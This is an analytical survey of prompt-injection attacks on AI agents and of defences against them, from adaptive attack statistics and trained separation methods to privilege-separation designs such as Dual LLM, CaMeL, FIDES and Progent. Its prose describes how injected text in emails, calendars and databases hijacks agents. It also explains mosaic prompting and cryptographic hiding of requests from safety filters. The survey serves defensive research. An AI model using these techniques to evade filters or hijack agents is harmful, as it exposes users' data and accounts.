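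These are large improvements, and unlike most of the twelve defences, both methods faced adaptive attacks in their original tests. But the people who built the defences also ran those attacks. Neither design sets a limit on what a better attack could achieve, so reducing the success rate from 96% to 3% does not close the class of attack.

### Repeated attempts

In late 2025, the security firm Gray Swan found that a single strong attack succeeded 4.7% of the time against Anthropic's Claude Opus 4.5, according to The Decoder's *Claude Opus 4.5 resists prompt injections better than rivals*. The success rate rose to 33.6% with ten attempts and 63.0% with a hundred. Competing models did worse, with rates as high as 92%.

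If each attempt had the same independent chance p of success, as in the earlier example of a hundred malicious emails, the chance of at least one success in k attempts would be

1 − (1 − p)^k

With p = 0.047, this gives 38% for ten attempts and 99% for a hundred. The first figure is close to the measured rate, but the second is far too high.

The formula fails because some test cases are much harder than others. If an attack has failed ninety times on one case, that case is probably hard, so the next ten attempts are less likely to work than the first ten were. Whenever p varies between cases, using its average in the formula overstates the chance of success over several attempts.

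A simple statistical model shows how large the effect can be. Suppose that attacks never succeed in 37% of cases, and that each attempt has a 7.5% chance of success in the other 63%. The average success rate for a single attempt is still 4.7%, but the model now predicts 34% for ten attempts and 63% for a hundred, almost exactly what Gray Swan measured. Three data points can't prove this explanation is right. A better attack, or a thousandth attempt, might also succeed in the remaining 37%.

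Narisetty and colleagues quote the same three figures but describe them as results for coding agents. The setting matters, as tests of the next version, Claude Opus 4.6, showed. VentureBeat reported from the model's February 2026 system card, Anthropic's published test results, that an attack in a restricted coding environment failed in all 200 attempts. When the model operated a graphical interface, the attack succeeded 17.8% of the time on the first attempt and 78.6% by the 200th. Anthropic's additional safeguards lowered the 200-attempt rate to 57.1%.

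Newer models resist attacks much better. The Decoder reported that in a general Gray Swan test with 15 attempts, the success rate fell from 5.5% for Claude Opus 4.8 to 2.0% for Claude Opus 5. No attack succeeded against Opus 5 in 129 browser scenarios. The Opus 4.5 test used different numbers of attempts, and perhaps different attacks, so its 33.6% success rate is not directly comparable with the 2.0% for Opus 5. Anthropic's *System Card* (2026) for Claude Opus 5.5, published in September, reports results similar to or better than those of Opus 5 on every prompt injection test, but it also warns that the new model is more likely than earlier ones to follow some malicious instructions.

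Zero successes in 129 scenarios is impressive, but like a perfect score on AgentDojo, it doesn't show that the true success rate is zero. Even if the scenarios were a random sample, the rate could be as high as 2.3% at 95% confidence. Nasr and colleagues argue that a test can at most fail to break a defence. Proofs about a model's behaviour, known as certified robustness, are a separate line of research.

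### Building the boundary into the model

StruQ, one of the twelve defences, borrows the idea behind parameterised queries. The application puts the instruction and the data in separate sections of the prompt, with reserved tokens marking where each begins. Ordinary software removes those tokens from the data, so an attacker cannot forge a boundary. The developers train the model to answer only the real instruction, using examples with other instructions planted in the data section.

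SecAlign keeps this layout but changes the training. Each training example pairs an answer that follows the user's instruction with one that follows the injected instruction. Training makes the first answer more likely relative to the second. MetaSecAlign is a later model from the same line of work.

The software that removes the reserved tokens guarantees that attackers can't write the marker. But StruQ's model processes the instruction and the data with the same network, and StruQ relies on training to make the model treat them differently, whereas a database never parses a bound value as SQL. Narisetty and colleagues cite a study in which an adaptive attack using gradients succeeded against StruQ almost every time on one benchmark and 80% to 100% of the time on another. For SecAlign the figures were 88% and 46%. Gradient attacks need the model's weights, which a company can keep secret,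 but Nasr and colleagues defeated MetaSecAlign with a search that did not need gradients.

Other researchers have changed how the model represents its input. A language model first converts each token into a list of numbers called an embedding. Normally, the word "delete" has the same embedding in a user's request as in a stranger's email. In 2025, Egor Zverev and colleagues proposed ASIDE, an architecture that rotates the embeddings of data tokens by 90 degrees, so that each pair of numbers (x, y) becomes (−y, x). Developers then train the model in the usual way. The rotation marks which tokens are data, and an attacker can't remove the mark because the application decides which tokens to rotate.

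The rotation gives the network a much clearer signal than a marker at the start of a passage, and ASIDE reports better separation and fewer successful injections. But the rotation discards no information, and everything after that first step is still learned. The later layers have to process the data to summarise it or answer questions about it, and nothing in the arithmetic stops the model from also following a command in the data.

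A strict boundary is difficult because the assistant's task requires it to act on what it reads. If an email mentions that a meeting has moved to Thursday, a good assistant should adjust, for instance by proposing a different time for lunch. The boundary would have to let that fact influence the assistant's actions but block a sentence asking it to move the meeting. People often phrase requests as facts and facts as requests, so wording alone isn't enough to tell them apart.

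Zverev and colleagues have also proposed a way to measure separation. They take a task and a passage of data, and add a short extra question whose answer is easy to recognise. In one run the question is part of the instruction, and in the other it is part of the data. The score counts only cases in which the model answers the question when it is in the instruction:

separation = cases where the model ignores the question in the data ÷ all cases where it answers the question in the instruction

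A model that always distinguished data from instructions would score 100%. The score excludes questions the model can't answer at all, so a weak model gets no credit for ignoring them. Narisetty and colleagues summarise the result this way: current models have no usable separation between data and instructions, and neither prompting nor fine-tuning reliably creates it. The test questions are harmless and don't adapt, so even a high score would be little evidence that a model could resist a determined attacker. A low score is more informative because it means the model confuses data with instructions even when nobody is trying to trick it.

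### Theoretical limits on filtering by meaning

Two theoretical papers argue that some filter failures are unavoidable. Both are mainly about harmful content, so they apply more to jailbreaks than to hijacked tool calls.

*LLM Censorship* (Glukhov et al., 2023) distinguishes filters that judge a text's form from filters that judge its meaning. It argues that filtering by meaning is impossible in general because models follow instructions so flexibly. A user can ask the model to encode its answer, and a filter that can't decode the answer can't judge its meaning. The answer may also be a computer program, and whether a program will ever do a particular harmful thing is undecidable, which means that no procedure can answer the question correctly for every program.

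In mosaic prompting, a user asks for harmless pieces and assembles them into something harmful. Someone who wants ransomware could ask separately for code that lists the files in a folder, code that encrypts a file and code that displays a message. Programmers need all of these for legitimate reasons, so a filter that checks each answer separately has no basis for blocking any of them.

Undecidability rules out a filter that classifies every text correctly, but a filter can still reject everything it can't verify. Rust's compiler does this, and so rejects some safe programs. The same policy would make a general assistant much less useful, because a filter can verify very little free prose. Glukhov and colleagues conclude that developers should treat harmful output as a computer security problem and adapt classical security methods to it.

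Ball, Gluch and colleagues (2025), in *On the Impossibility of Separating Intelligence from Judgment*, use cryptography to show that some attacks can hide from any filter that is much faster than the model. Their proof relies on time-lock puzzles, which are quick to create but slow to solve. In the classic version, the creator chooses a number x and a modulus N, which is the product of two large secret primes, and asks for the value of

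x^(2^t) mod N

Someone who knows the primes can take a shortcut. As far as anyone knows, everybody else has to square x t times in a row, and extra processors don't help.

The attack then has three steps:

1. The attacker encrypts a harmful request so that only the puzzle's solution unlocks it.
2. The attacker hides the puzzle and the encrypted request in innocent-looking text. A language model normally writes by choosing at random among likely next words. Here, the hidden message takes the place of the random numbers, so the text looks like any other text from that model.
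3. The target model recovers the message from the choice of words, solves the puzzle and carries out the request.

A filter with much less computing time than the target model can't solve the puzzle, so it can't tell this prompt from an innocent one. Ball and colleagues prove a related result for filters on outputs. For some model and some definition of harm, no efficient filter works, even if it has more computing time than the model.

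The proofs assume that time-lock puzzles are as hard as cryptographers believe. The result about prompts also assumes that innocent prompts vary enough to hide a message in, and that the filter has no access to the model's internals. Most importantly, it concerns a model that decodes and follows hidden messages. Ball and colleagues acknowledge that such a model may be contrived, but point out that contrived weaknesses in cryptography have later led to real thefts.

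They conclude that filters outside a model cannot make it safe, but their theorems support only the narrower claim that no fast filter works for every possible model. A filter may still work well for a particular model, though guaranteeing this would require some knowledge of how that model behaves. The theorems do not rule out monitors that read a model's internal activations, and they do not apply to rules that do not depend on meaning, such as a ban on payments to new accounts.

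### The value of imperfect defences

Reducing the success rate of attacks can prevent a lot of harm even if some still get through. In Anthropic's browser tests, an adaptive attacker had 100 attempts in each environment. Against Claude Opus 4.5 alone, 8.0% of attacks succeeded, and improved safeguards cut this to 1.4%. For Claude Sonnet 4.5, a smaller model, the rate fell from 13.8% to 1.9%. If a thousand Opus 4.5 users each faced one such attack, the expected number of victims would fall from 80 to 14.

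Filters can also be worthwhile even when a skilled attacker can beat them. VentureBeat reports that Meta's LlamaFirewall, which combines a version of PromptGuard with a second model that audits the agent, reduced attack success on AgentDojo from 17.6% to 1.75%. Nasr and colleagues got past PromptGuard more than 90% of the time. Both results can be useful to a company deciding whether to install such a filter, because many real attackers copy known attacks and never test them against the defence. Nasr and colleagues regard filters as a useful but limited part of a broader defence.

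A filter that catches more attacks also blocks more legitimate work. Anthropic released Opus 5.5 with a temporarily wider safety margin against jailbreaks while it worked to reduce false alarms from its classifiers.

The benefit of a lower attack success rate depends on how much damage one success can do. If each successful attack costs one user a small, recoverable sum, cutting the rate by four-fifths cuts the losses by about the same proportion. Developers can reduce the losses further by limiting attempts and investigating failed ones. But if one success is enough to publish a company's customer database, a lower rate helps less, because the attacker can make many attempts and needs only one to work.

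## How does separating privileges keep injected text from choosing actions?

When one successful attack can do serious damage, it makes sense to limit what a deceived model can do. The governing principle of Beurer-Kellner and colleagues is that untrusted input must not be able to trigger consequential actions, meaning those that harm the system or its environment. At a minimum, an agent that has read such input must have no tool that could corrupt or disclose data. Its output must also be safe for whoever receives it, so it can't include a link that leaks private data or text that hijacks the agent in a later session.

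Four of their designs apply the principle by controlling which text a model can see when it makes a decision. The other two, action selection and map-reduce, work mainly by restricting what a model may output. In one of their examples, which suits all four designs, a user tells an assistant with access to mail and a calendar to "send today's schedule to my boss John Doe". An attacker has sent the user a calendar invitation with instructions hidden in the description. An ordinary agent reads the calendar, including the hidden instructions, and then decides what to do next, with all its tools still available.

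### Privilege separation in operating systems

Operating systems had a similar problem with programs that need special privileges but also handle data from strangers. OpenSSH, which lets people log in to a computer over a network, needs full control of the machine for a few operations, such as opening a terminal for a new user. It also has to interpret data sent by anyone on the internet. When a single process did both jobs, a bug in the code that read network data could give a stranger full control of the machine.

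Provos, Friedl and Honeyman (2003), in *Preventing Privilege Escalation*, describe how they split OpenSSH in two. A child process without special privileges handles all the network traffic. A privileged process, the monitor, checks whether each request from the child is allowed at that stage of the login. If it is, the monitor carries it out, and if not, the monitor shuts down. The split stopped attackers from taking over the machine through bugs that had let them do so in earlier versions, including some that nobody knew about when the team wrote the new code.

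An attacker who takes over the child can still send requests to the monitor, so Provos and colleagues limited what the child can request. For example, it can request a signature made with the machine's private key, but not the key itself.

The model that reads untrusted text corresponds to OpenSSH's unprivileged child process. That process needs only a short list of precisely defined requests, but an assistant's work involves passing prose along. If that prose reaches a second model that has tools, the second model may follow instructions injected into it.

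### A plan fixed in advance

The simplest of the four designs is plan-then-execute. The model first sees only the user's request and the descriptions of its tools, and commits to a list of calls:

```
1. calendar.read(today)
2. email.write(to = "john.doe@company.com", body = ____)
```

Ordinary software then works through the list. After the first call, the model reads the calendar and fills in the blank. By then it has also read the attacker's text, but the software will run only the next call on the list, which sends one email to John Doe at the address already written there.

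The attacker can't add a call or redirect the email, but can rewrite its entire body. John Doe might receive a false schedule, or a request, seemingly from the user, to approve a payment.

The recipient is safe only because the planner had the address before it read the calendar. The address has to come from the user or from an address book that outsiders can't edit. If the plan left the address blank as well, the attacker could fill it in.

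Beurer-Kellner and colleagues compare this protection to control-flow integrity, a defence for ordinary programs. A running program often computes which instruction to jump to next, and an attacker who corrupts its memory can redirect the jump. In *Control-Flow Integrity*, Abadi, Budiu and colleagues (2005) work out beforehand which jumps a program may make, then add checks that keep it to those paths. The protection holds even if the attacker controls all the program's data memory. Abadi and colleagues caution that it doesn't stop attacks that stay on the permitted paths, such as using a malformed argument to make the program launch a dangerous file. The body of John Doe's email is this kind of argument.

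How much damage an argument can do depends on the tool that receives it. Beurer-Kellner and colleagues discuss a file assistant that has committed to using only a search command and a move command. Both are routine, but an injection could still make the assistant search for sensitive files and move them to a public network drive. A list of permitted commands gives little protection if the commands are powerful and their arguments are unrestricted.

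### Two models and a controller

Willison (2023), in *The Dual LLM pattern for building AI assistants*, proposed separating the planner from the reader altogether. The privileged model takes the user's request and has the tools, but never reads untrusted text. The quarantined model reads untrusted text but has no tools, and the designer assumes that it could turn hostile at any moment. A controller, which is ordinary software, passes material between them and runs the tools. The schedule request would go like this:

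1. The controller gives the request to the privileged model, which asks for today's calendar.
2. The controller fetches the calendar and stores it under the name `$VAR1`. It tells the privileged model the name but not the contents.
3. The privileged model asks for `$VAR1` to be formatted as an email. The controller puts the calendar text in place of the name, sends it to the quarantined model and stores the reply as `$VAR2`.
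4. The privileged model requests an email to John Doe with `$VAR2` as the body. The controller swaps in the stored text at the moment of the call and sends the email.

The variable works much like the placeholder in a parameterised query. The privileged model chooses the structure of the action without seeing the value, so the value can't alter that structure. Costa and colleagues use the same technique in a planner that looks up each variable just before a tool runs. Their software can also prevent the model from naming variables that don't exist.

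A database stores a bound value unchanged, though, while the quarantined model interprets the calendar and writes something new. The attacker may therefore control everything in `$VAR2`. In the schedule example, that is still the body of an email to the boss, but other requests carry more risk.

One risk is that injected text can leak private data without changing the agent's planned calls. *On the Relative Security of Prompt Injection* (2026) gives the example of a plan that reads a user's private notes and an email from an attacker, has the quarantined model draft a reply using both, and sends the reply to the attacker. An injection in the email makes the quarantined model quote the notes in the reply, so the attacker receives them when the agent sends it as planned.

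Another risk arises when the recipient is a variable. Willison (2025), in *CaMeL offers a promising new direction for mitigating prompt injection attacks*, credits researchers at Google DeepMind with finding this flaw in the pattern. In their example, the user asks the assistant to send Bob a document at the address given in the meeting notes. The quarantined model has to extract the address, so anyone who can edit the notes can replace it with their own. The schedule request would have the same weakness if the user asked to send it to "whoever is chairing the three o'clock meeting".

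Willison called the original proposal "pretty bad" from the start. It makes an assistant more complicated to build and less pleasant to use, and a single mistake that lets untrusted text reach the privileged model undoes the protection. The design also treats everything the user types as trusted, including text pasted from elsewhere. The quarantined model's output may also appear on the user's screen and could persuade the user to copy private data into an attacker's website.

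### A plan written as code

Google DeepMind's own system, CaMeL (2025), develops the two-model design further by having the privileged model write a program. Beurer-Kellner and colleagues call this general approach code-then-execute. For the schedule, the program might be:

```
schedule = read_calendar("today")
body = ask_quarantined_model("Format this as an email", schedule)
send_email(recipient="john.doe@company.com", body=body)
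```

The privileged model writes this whole program from the user's request and the tool descriptions. An interpreter, which is ordinary software, then runs the program and makes the tool calls. The quarantined model sees the calendar only when the second line runs, and its answer goes into the variable `body`. *CaMeLoT* (Nikolaou, Eckhoff and colleagues, 2026) explains that an injection reaching the quarantined model can change the value of `body` but can't send instructions back to the privileged model.

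The language is a restricted form of Python, which current models already write well. It leaves out some features, such as open-ended loops, but a program can still repeat a step for each item in a list or take different actions under different conditions.

Code also shows which values came from which. CaMeL's interpreter tags each value with its sources and who may read it. Before every tool call, a policy written as a short Python function checks the tool, its arguments and their tags, then allows or refuses the call. A policy can therefore block an email, or ask the user to approve it, if the recipient's address came from a calendar entry. Willison warns that someone has to write and maintain the policies, and that users who face too many approval requests start agreeing to everything.

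The split can also improve privacy. Extracting an address is easier than writing a program, so the quarantined model could be a small one that runs on the user's computer. The company that hosts the privileged model would then see the request to send the schedule, but not the schedule itself.

*Can CaMeLs Talk?* (Peters-Gill, Semler and colleagues, 2026) adapts control-flow integrity to such agents. It defines a control-flow plan as a program that determines which tools to call, and in what order, given the values earlier steps return. An agent has control-flow integrity if it follows a plan made only from the user's instruction and other trusted information. Untrusted data can then select among the plan's branches but can't add new ones.

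Injected text can still influence which branch of a plan the assistant follows. Suppose the user asks the assistant to copy in the travel office if the schedule includes a trip. An attacker who adds a fake trip to the calendar can make the assistant send the schedule to the travel office. *CaMeLs Can Use Computers Too* (2026), which applies the two-model design to agents that operate a computer screen, calls this branch steering. For instance, a fake button on a web page can lead the model that interprets the screen to take a dangerous path that the plan allows. Adding branches helps an agent handle more situations but also gives an attacker more paths to choose from.

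The guarantee can fail when one agent gives instructions to another. Peters-Gill and colleagues connected three CaMeL agents: an orchestrator, an agent that queried a database and an agent that sent notifications. They ran them without data policies to test the protection of the plan alone. The user asked them to send a colleague a summary of job applicants on Slack. The database contained an injected instruction to email the data to an outside address. The first two agents followed their plans, but the orchestrator put the summary into the sentence it sent to the notification agent, which treated the whole sentence as its user's request. That agent's privileged model read the injection and added the email to its plan.

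This is the same problem as with pasted text, except that a program does the pasting. Peters-Gill and colleagues prove that, under mild assumptions, if agents in a hierarchy call one another this way and any tool returns untrusted data, the system as a whole lacks control-flow integrity, even if every agent has it individually. They propose sending instructions and data through separate channels, so that the second agent's planner never reads the data.

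In *AI Agents, Conversations, and Information Flow*, Garby, Gordon and Sands (2026) object to building a fixed pair of models into the architecture. In their programming language, a program can copy the current conversation, have a model read something in the copy, and then discard the copy, keeping only a labelled result. The program can therefore isolate a model only when a task requires it.

### Removing the user's own text

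Plan-then-execute, the two-model design and CaMeL all treat the user's request as trusted. Context minimisation is for cases where the user is hostile or has unknowingly pasted in hostile text. The system uses the request for one step and then removes it from the model's context.

In the car dealer's chatbot, the model first turns the customer's message into a database query for current offers. The software runs the query and deletes the message. The model then writes its reply from the query results, without seeing any demand for a discount that the message contained.

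In the schedule example, suppose the user's request includes a passage copied from a malicious web page. One call to the model turns the request into a calendar query. The software then discards the request, and a second call formats the results as an email. The pasted passage can't control the wording of the email, but it can still affect the query, perhaps so that it fetches a month of appointments instead of a day. It can also affect the recipient if the first call chooses that too. Context minimisation also doesn't stop injections in the calendar itself.

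Anything the first step passes on can carry an attack. Beurer-Kellner and colleagues consider a medical chatbot that summarises a patient's symptoms, gets a diagnosis from a database or a doctor, and explains it to the patient. If the software deletes the patient's message but keeps the summary, an injection could survive in the summary and influence the explanation. Deleting the summary as well prevents this, but then the chatbot can't relate its explanation to anything the patient said. Even then, a false summary could still lead to a wrong diagnosis.

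Another chatbot answers questions about medicines by showing passages from official leaflets. If the software displays only those passages, all the text is genuine, but a user could still manipulate the search to leave out the warnings.

### Tasks that depend on what the agent reads

The schedule is a convenient example because the assistant can decide what to do before opening the calendar. Costa and colleagues make this property precise. They define a task by the user's request, the available tools and a set D of possible states of the data, such as all the calendars the user might have. For each state d, let S(d) be the set of action sequences that would complete the task, where a sequence consists of tool calls followed by a final response. The task is data-independent if

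⋂<sub>d ∈ D</sub> S(d) ≠ ∅

In words, at least one sequence works whatever the data turn out to be. If no such sequence exists, the task is data-dependent.

Sending the schedule is data-independent because the same steps of reading the calendar, formatting it and emailing the result work for any calendar, as long as a variable stands in for the text. Costa and colleagues contrast this with a request to read the three latest emails and create a calendar event if one of them proposes a meeting. The call that creates an event is correct only if there is a proposal, so no fixed list of calls is right in both cases, and a planner given only a variable's name can't determine which case applies.

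A program can handle this task by having the quarantined model check whether the emails propose a meeting, and creating the event only if the answer is yes. FIDES, the planner that Costa and colleagues built, does something similar by passing the privileged model a yes-or-no answer. An attacker can choose the answer and fill in the details of the event, but can't make the agent do anything else.

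Even a program with conditions can't handle some tasks. *Securing Web Agents with the Compile-Then-Execute Paradigm* (Chow, Zhu and colleagues, 2026) gives the example of a user who asks an agent to find an email from the boss and do whatever it says. Nobody can list the required actions in advance because they depend on the email, but the design forbids text the agent reads from choosing its actions. Even when a mail server can verify the sender's address, trusting the boss's emails is risky because the boss may have forwarded something a stranger wrote.

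How often such tasks come up depends on the work. Costa and colleagues sorted the 97 user tasks in AgentDojo:

| Setting | Data-independent, no model reads the data | Data-independent, with a quarantined model | Data-dependent |
|---|---|---|---|
| Workspace | 47.5% | 47.5% | 5.0% |
| Travel | 0% | 90.0% | 10.0% |
| Banking | 18.7% | 37.5% | 43.8% |
| Slack | 19.0% | 38.1% | 42.9% |

About a fifth of all the tasks are data-dependent. Many of the banking tasks ask the agent to open a file and follow the instructions in it.

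Results are more favourable on WebArena, a benchmark of website tasks. *Web Agents Should Adopt the Compile-and-Execute Paradigm* (2026) finds that a program written in advance could handle every task, and that 81% need no language model while the program runs. The two analyses count differently, because Costa and colleagues class a task that needs a condition as data-dependent, whereas a program written in advance can include conditions. Benchmark tasks also tend to have clear goals so that a computer can grade them. People probably give their assistants vaguer jobs, such as dealing with the morning's email, and more of those would depend on what the agent finds.

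The WebArena result also assumes that each website offers a complete and trustworthy set of operations for programs to call, which few do. An agent that works by clicking has to look at a page to know what a click will do, so it can't plan its clicks beforehand. Chow and colleagues built the missing interfaces for their own web agent, Baya, by hand from each site's existing functions, and automated the browser where those functions weren't enough.

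### When a plan fails

A plan made without seeing the data will sometimes be wrong. The documentation for one of the shopping sites that Chow and colleagues used describes product options as optional, but adding shoes to the basket fails without a size and colour. The available sizes differ from shoe to shoe, so the program has to look them up first.

*Architecting Resilient LLM Agents* (2025), a guide to plan-then-execute designs, calls a one-shot plan brittle and recommends having a model review the plan after each step and rewrite it if necessary. Replanning makes the agent more reliable, but it removes the protection of a fixed plan if the reviewing model reads tool output, because an injection in that output can influence the new plan.

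Baya rewrites its program only after a failure. The model that writes the code gets the old program and a restricted error report, with no content from the website. It can then correct some misused operations, but it can't add an operation that the interface lacks. An attacker may be able to cause a failure but can't put a message in the report. It is unclear how far an agent can recover with so little information. *Securing Computer-Use Agents Against Branch Steering Attacks* (2026) lists as an open problem how to recover from unexpected states without weakening the boundary around the planner.

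Software engineering is especially hard to plan in advance because a programmer fixing a bug reads some code, runs a test, sees it fail, revises the theory and tries again. In *Twin Agent*, Hu, Jacob and colleagues (2026) argue that designs which plan first don't suit this work, and propose passing a small amount of information between two agents at every step. One agent reads everything, including bug reports from strangers, but can't act. It sends short hints to a second agent, which can change the code but never sees the bug reports. The software blocks or shortens hints that exceed a set length and runs a filter on the rest.

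Hu and colleagues have observed that attacks on the strongest current models tend to need long texts, so they explicitly assume that a short hint is unlikely to take over Twin Agent's second agent. Software can enforce a length limit, but the assumption is about how a model behaves, and a better attack or a different model could prove it wrong. If a short hint does succeed, the second agent can do whatever its tools permit. Twin Agent therefore makes hijacking harder but still possible, whereas a fixed plan keeps injected text from adding a call even if the model that reads it follows the injected instructions.

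## How do labels and policies control where data may go?

An agent that keeps to a fixed plan can still do damage, because injected text can fill in the body of an email and a call the plan allows can send private notes to the wrong person. To prevent this, the software around the model has to track where each value came from and who may see it. Information-flow control, an idea that is fifty years old, does this by labelling data with its origin and secrecy, carrying the labels through every computation and checking them before each action. CaMeL's tags are a recent example.

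### Denning's lattice and Biba's rules

Ordinary access control limits who may open a file, but not what happens to its contents afterwards. A program that can read a secret file can copy the contents into a file that everyone can open. In *A Lattice Model of Secure Information Flow*, Denning (1976) proposed controlling the flow of the information itself.

Every piece of data in Denning's model has a label. In modern notation, A ⊑ B means that information labelled A may flow to a place labelled B. For example, public ⊑ secret, because a secret file may contain public information. Secret information may not flow to a public file. The relation has to be transitive, since a program that copies a to b and then b to c has in effect copied a to c.

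When a program combines two inputs, the result gets their join, written A ⊔ B. This is the lowest label that both inputs may flow to, which means that:

- A ⊑ A ⊔ B and B ⊑ A ⊔ B. Without this rule, anyone could publish a secret number by adding zero to it.
- If A ⊑ C and B ⊑ C, then A ⊔ B ⊑ C. This keeps the label from being higher than it needs to be.

A finite set of labels with a lowest label and a join for every pair forms a lattice, hence Denning's title.

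Secrecy labels don't protect against forged or malicious data, which is the main worry with prompt injection. In 1977 Kenneth Biba published a matching set of rules for integrity, meaning how far data can be trusted. In one version, a program's integrity level drops to that of the least trustworthy thing it has read, and it may change only things at or below its current level. Narisetty and colleagues apply these rules to agents. Reading a stranger's email lowers the agent's level, after which the agent may not authorise a payment.

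In the same notation, trusted ⊑ untrusted, which means that trusted data may go wherever untrusted data may, but not the reverse.

FIDES, from Costa and colleagues, gives each piece of data an integrity label and a confidentiality label. Data may flow to a place only if both of its labels are at or below the corresponding labels there, so data labelled "trusted, secret" may not flow to a place labelled "untrusted, public", nor may data flow in the opposite direction. The table shows what happens when an agent combines a user's request, a record from the company's database and a page from the public web.

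| What the agent combines | Join of the labels | May the result trigger a payment? | May the result go on a public website? |
|---|---|---|---|
| The request alone | Trusted, public | Yes | Yes |
| The request and the company record | Trusted, secret | Yes | No |
| The request and the web page | Untrusted, public | No | Yes |
| The company record and the web page | Untrusted, secret | No | No |

A secrecy label can also be a list of permitted readers. The join of two such labels is the overlap between their lists. If Ann, Bob and Carol may read one document, and Bob, Carol and Dan may read another, only Bob and Carol may read a summary of both.

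### How FIDES handles a request

Suppose a user asks an agent to summarise recent emails about Project X and send the summary to the user's manager. One of the emails contains an injected instruction to forward the top message in the mailbox to an outsider. FIDES would deal with the request like this:

1. The user's message enters the conversation as trusted and public, the default for anything the user or developer writes.
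2. The planning model asks for the emails. The mail tool returns a record for each one, with a label on every field. Suppose the dates are trusted and the text is untrusted.
3. FIDES compares each field's label with the label of the conversation so far. It leaves the dates in view, moves the text into variables and shows the planning model only their names. The conversation is still trusted.
4. The planning model asks a quarantined model to summarise the variables. The summary goes into a new variable, labelled with the join of everything that went into it, and is therefore untrusted.
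5. The planning model requests an email to the manager with the new variable as the body. FIDES swaps in the text, checks the labels against the policy for that tool and sends the email.

Costa and colleagues describe two basic policies for the check in step 5. Under the trusted-action policy, a consequential call goes ahead only if no untrusted data influenced it. The policy can apply to only some parts of a call. Here it would cover the decision to send and the choice of recipient, but not the body. Under the permitted-flow policy, data may go only to people already entitled to read it. This policy limits what an attacker can gain from an injection, but doesn't stop the injection from hijacking the agent.

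*Optimizing Agent Planning for Security and Autonomy* (Kolluri, Sharma and colleagues, 2026), a follow-up from Microsoft, allows a tool to send data out if it satisfies either policy. The tool may send the data if nothing untrusted influenced the decision, because the user presumably meant to share it. Otherwise, the recipients must already have access to the data.

The planning model can also open a variable and read it. The injected instruction then becomes part of the conversation, which is untrusted from that point on. If the model follows the instruction and tries to forward the message to the outsider, the call fails both policies, because untrusted text influenced the decision and the outsider isn't allowed to read the message. But the model could still forward it to a colleague who had already received it.

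Nobody can tell which parts of a model's input influenced its answer, so FIDES gives each answer the join of the labels on everything the model read. Without variables, a single email from a stranger would make every later step untrusted, and the agent could do little else for the rest of the task, a problem known as label creep. Hiding the text in variables keeps the planning model's integrity level from dropping.

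### FIDES on AgentDojo

Costa and colleagues tested FIDES on AgentDojo with an attacker who knew the names of the agent's tools. With GPT-4o and no policy checks, 152 attacks succeeded against a basic planner, which reads every tool result directly, and 21 succeeded against FIDES. With checks on, none succeeded against either planner, so the security comes from the checks. The variables in FIDES make the agent more useful while the checks are on.

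The figure of "none" comes from a manual review. AgentDojo's automatic scoring recorded three successful attacks against FIDES with checks on, but Costa and colleagues discounted them. Such discrepancies arose when AgentDojo counted as a success a call that the software had blocked, a message that the policies allowed, or a change to the text alone. An attacker who wanted to distort a summary might well consider a change to the text a success.

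These are the shares of legitimate tasks that GPT-4o completed when nobody was attacking:

| Setting | Basic planner, no checks | Basic planner, with checks | FIDES, with checks |
|---|---|---|---|
| Workspace | 75.0% | 37.0% | 59.0% |
| Travel | 70.0% | 73.0% | 41.0% |
| Banking | 98.8% | 37.5% | 52.5% |
| Slack | 93.3% | 20.0% | 47.6% |
| Average of the four | 84.3% | 41.9% | 50.0% |

Costa and colleagues report that FIDES completes 8% more tasks than a basic planner, or 16% more with OpenAI's o1, a stronger reasoning model. The averages in the table show that the 8% is a difference of eight percentage points and that the basic planner was under the same checks. FIDES with GPT-4o has a completion rate 34 points lower than an unprotected agent's.

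Part of that loss comes from the model confusing variables with one another, as GPT-4o sometimes did. With checks off, FIDES did 23.7 points worse than the basic planner with GPT-4o but only 6.3 points worse with o1. In the travel setting with checks on, switching to o1 raised FIDES's score from 41% to 68%. Both models are old, and current ones would probably lose less. But a better model can't recover tasks the policies are meant to block, such as the banking tasks that depend on instructions in a file.

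A planner that sees only some fields may also act on too little information. In one AgentDojo task, the agent must change the user's password if it finds a suspicious transaction. The agent could see amounts and dates, but the descriptions were hidden in variables. It judged a large payment suspicious without the descriptions and changed the password. AgentDojo counted this as a success, and no untrusted text had influenced the decision.

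The labels favoured the defence, because Costa and colleagues marked a field as untrusted if at least one AgentDojo attack used it. This allows a clean test of the mechanism, but a company installing such a system doesn't know in advance which fields attackers will use.

### Rules on individual calls

A simpler approach ignores where data came from and restricts the tool calls themselves. *Progent* (Shi, He and colleagues, 2025) describes a policy whose rules allow or forbid a tool call depending on its arguments. Before each call, ordinary software checks the rules for that tool, applying those that forbid before those that allow. If no rule matches, it blocks the call and returns the reason to the agent, so that the agent can try something else.

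Writing such rules by hand for every request is impractical, so a language model writes them from the user's request and revises them as the agent works. Suppose the user asks the agent to carry out a to-do list in an email from Alice. The first policy allows only a search for that email. One task on the list is to post a summary of recent emails to Slack, so the model proposes rules that let the agent read mail, look up Slack details and post messages. Once the agent has found the right Slack name, the model restricts posting to that name. If one of the recent emails contains an injected instruction to forward the inbox to an outsider, the model may propose a rule that allows this too.

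Alice's list and the injected instruction both reach the model as text in an email, so the model may not be able to tell a legitimate request for more permissions from a malicious one. Progent therefore compares each new policy with the old one using an SMT solver, a program that settles questions of logic. If A(P) is the set of calls that policy P allows, Progent applies a change from P to P′ automatically only when

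A(P′) ⊆ A(P)

A new policy needs approval if it allows anything the old one didn't. Between approvals, the agent's permissions therefore cannot grow, even if an injection has fully compromised the model that writes the policy.

The security then depends on who approves changes to the policy. Progent can refuse every change that widens the policy, accept them all or ask a person. Refusing them all would make Alice's to-do list impossible to complete, because the user's request never mentioned Slack. Accepting them all lets a model that has read the attacker's text grant the attacker's request. Shi and colleagues used that setting for most of their tests as a worst case, and attack success on AgentDojo still fell from 39.9% to 1.0%, though this measured rate does not guarantee security.

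*Extending the Formalism and Theoretical Foundations of Cryptography to AI* (2026) objects that Progent's automatic updates still depend on a model to filter out malicious instructions, and that people make mistakes when they write policies by hand. The solver meets the first objection only if Progent refuses every update that widens the policy or a reliable person reviews each one. Narisetty and colleagues raise a related concern by comparing these defences to a reference monitor, a component that checks every action against a policy, cannot be bypassed or altered, and is small enough to verify. Progent's checking code could meet that standard, but a language model that writes the policy is hard to verify.

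Rules on tool calls also don't account for where an argument came from. *Aligning Provenance with Authorization* (Wang, Li and Tian, 2026) gives the example of a user who asks an agent to book a flight and a hotel. An attacker has planted a fake flight code in a hotel listing. A rule that checks only the tool and the form of its arguments allows the booking, because the agent is permitted to book flights and the code has the right format.

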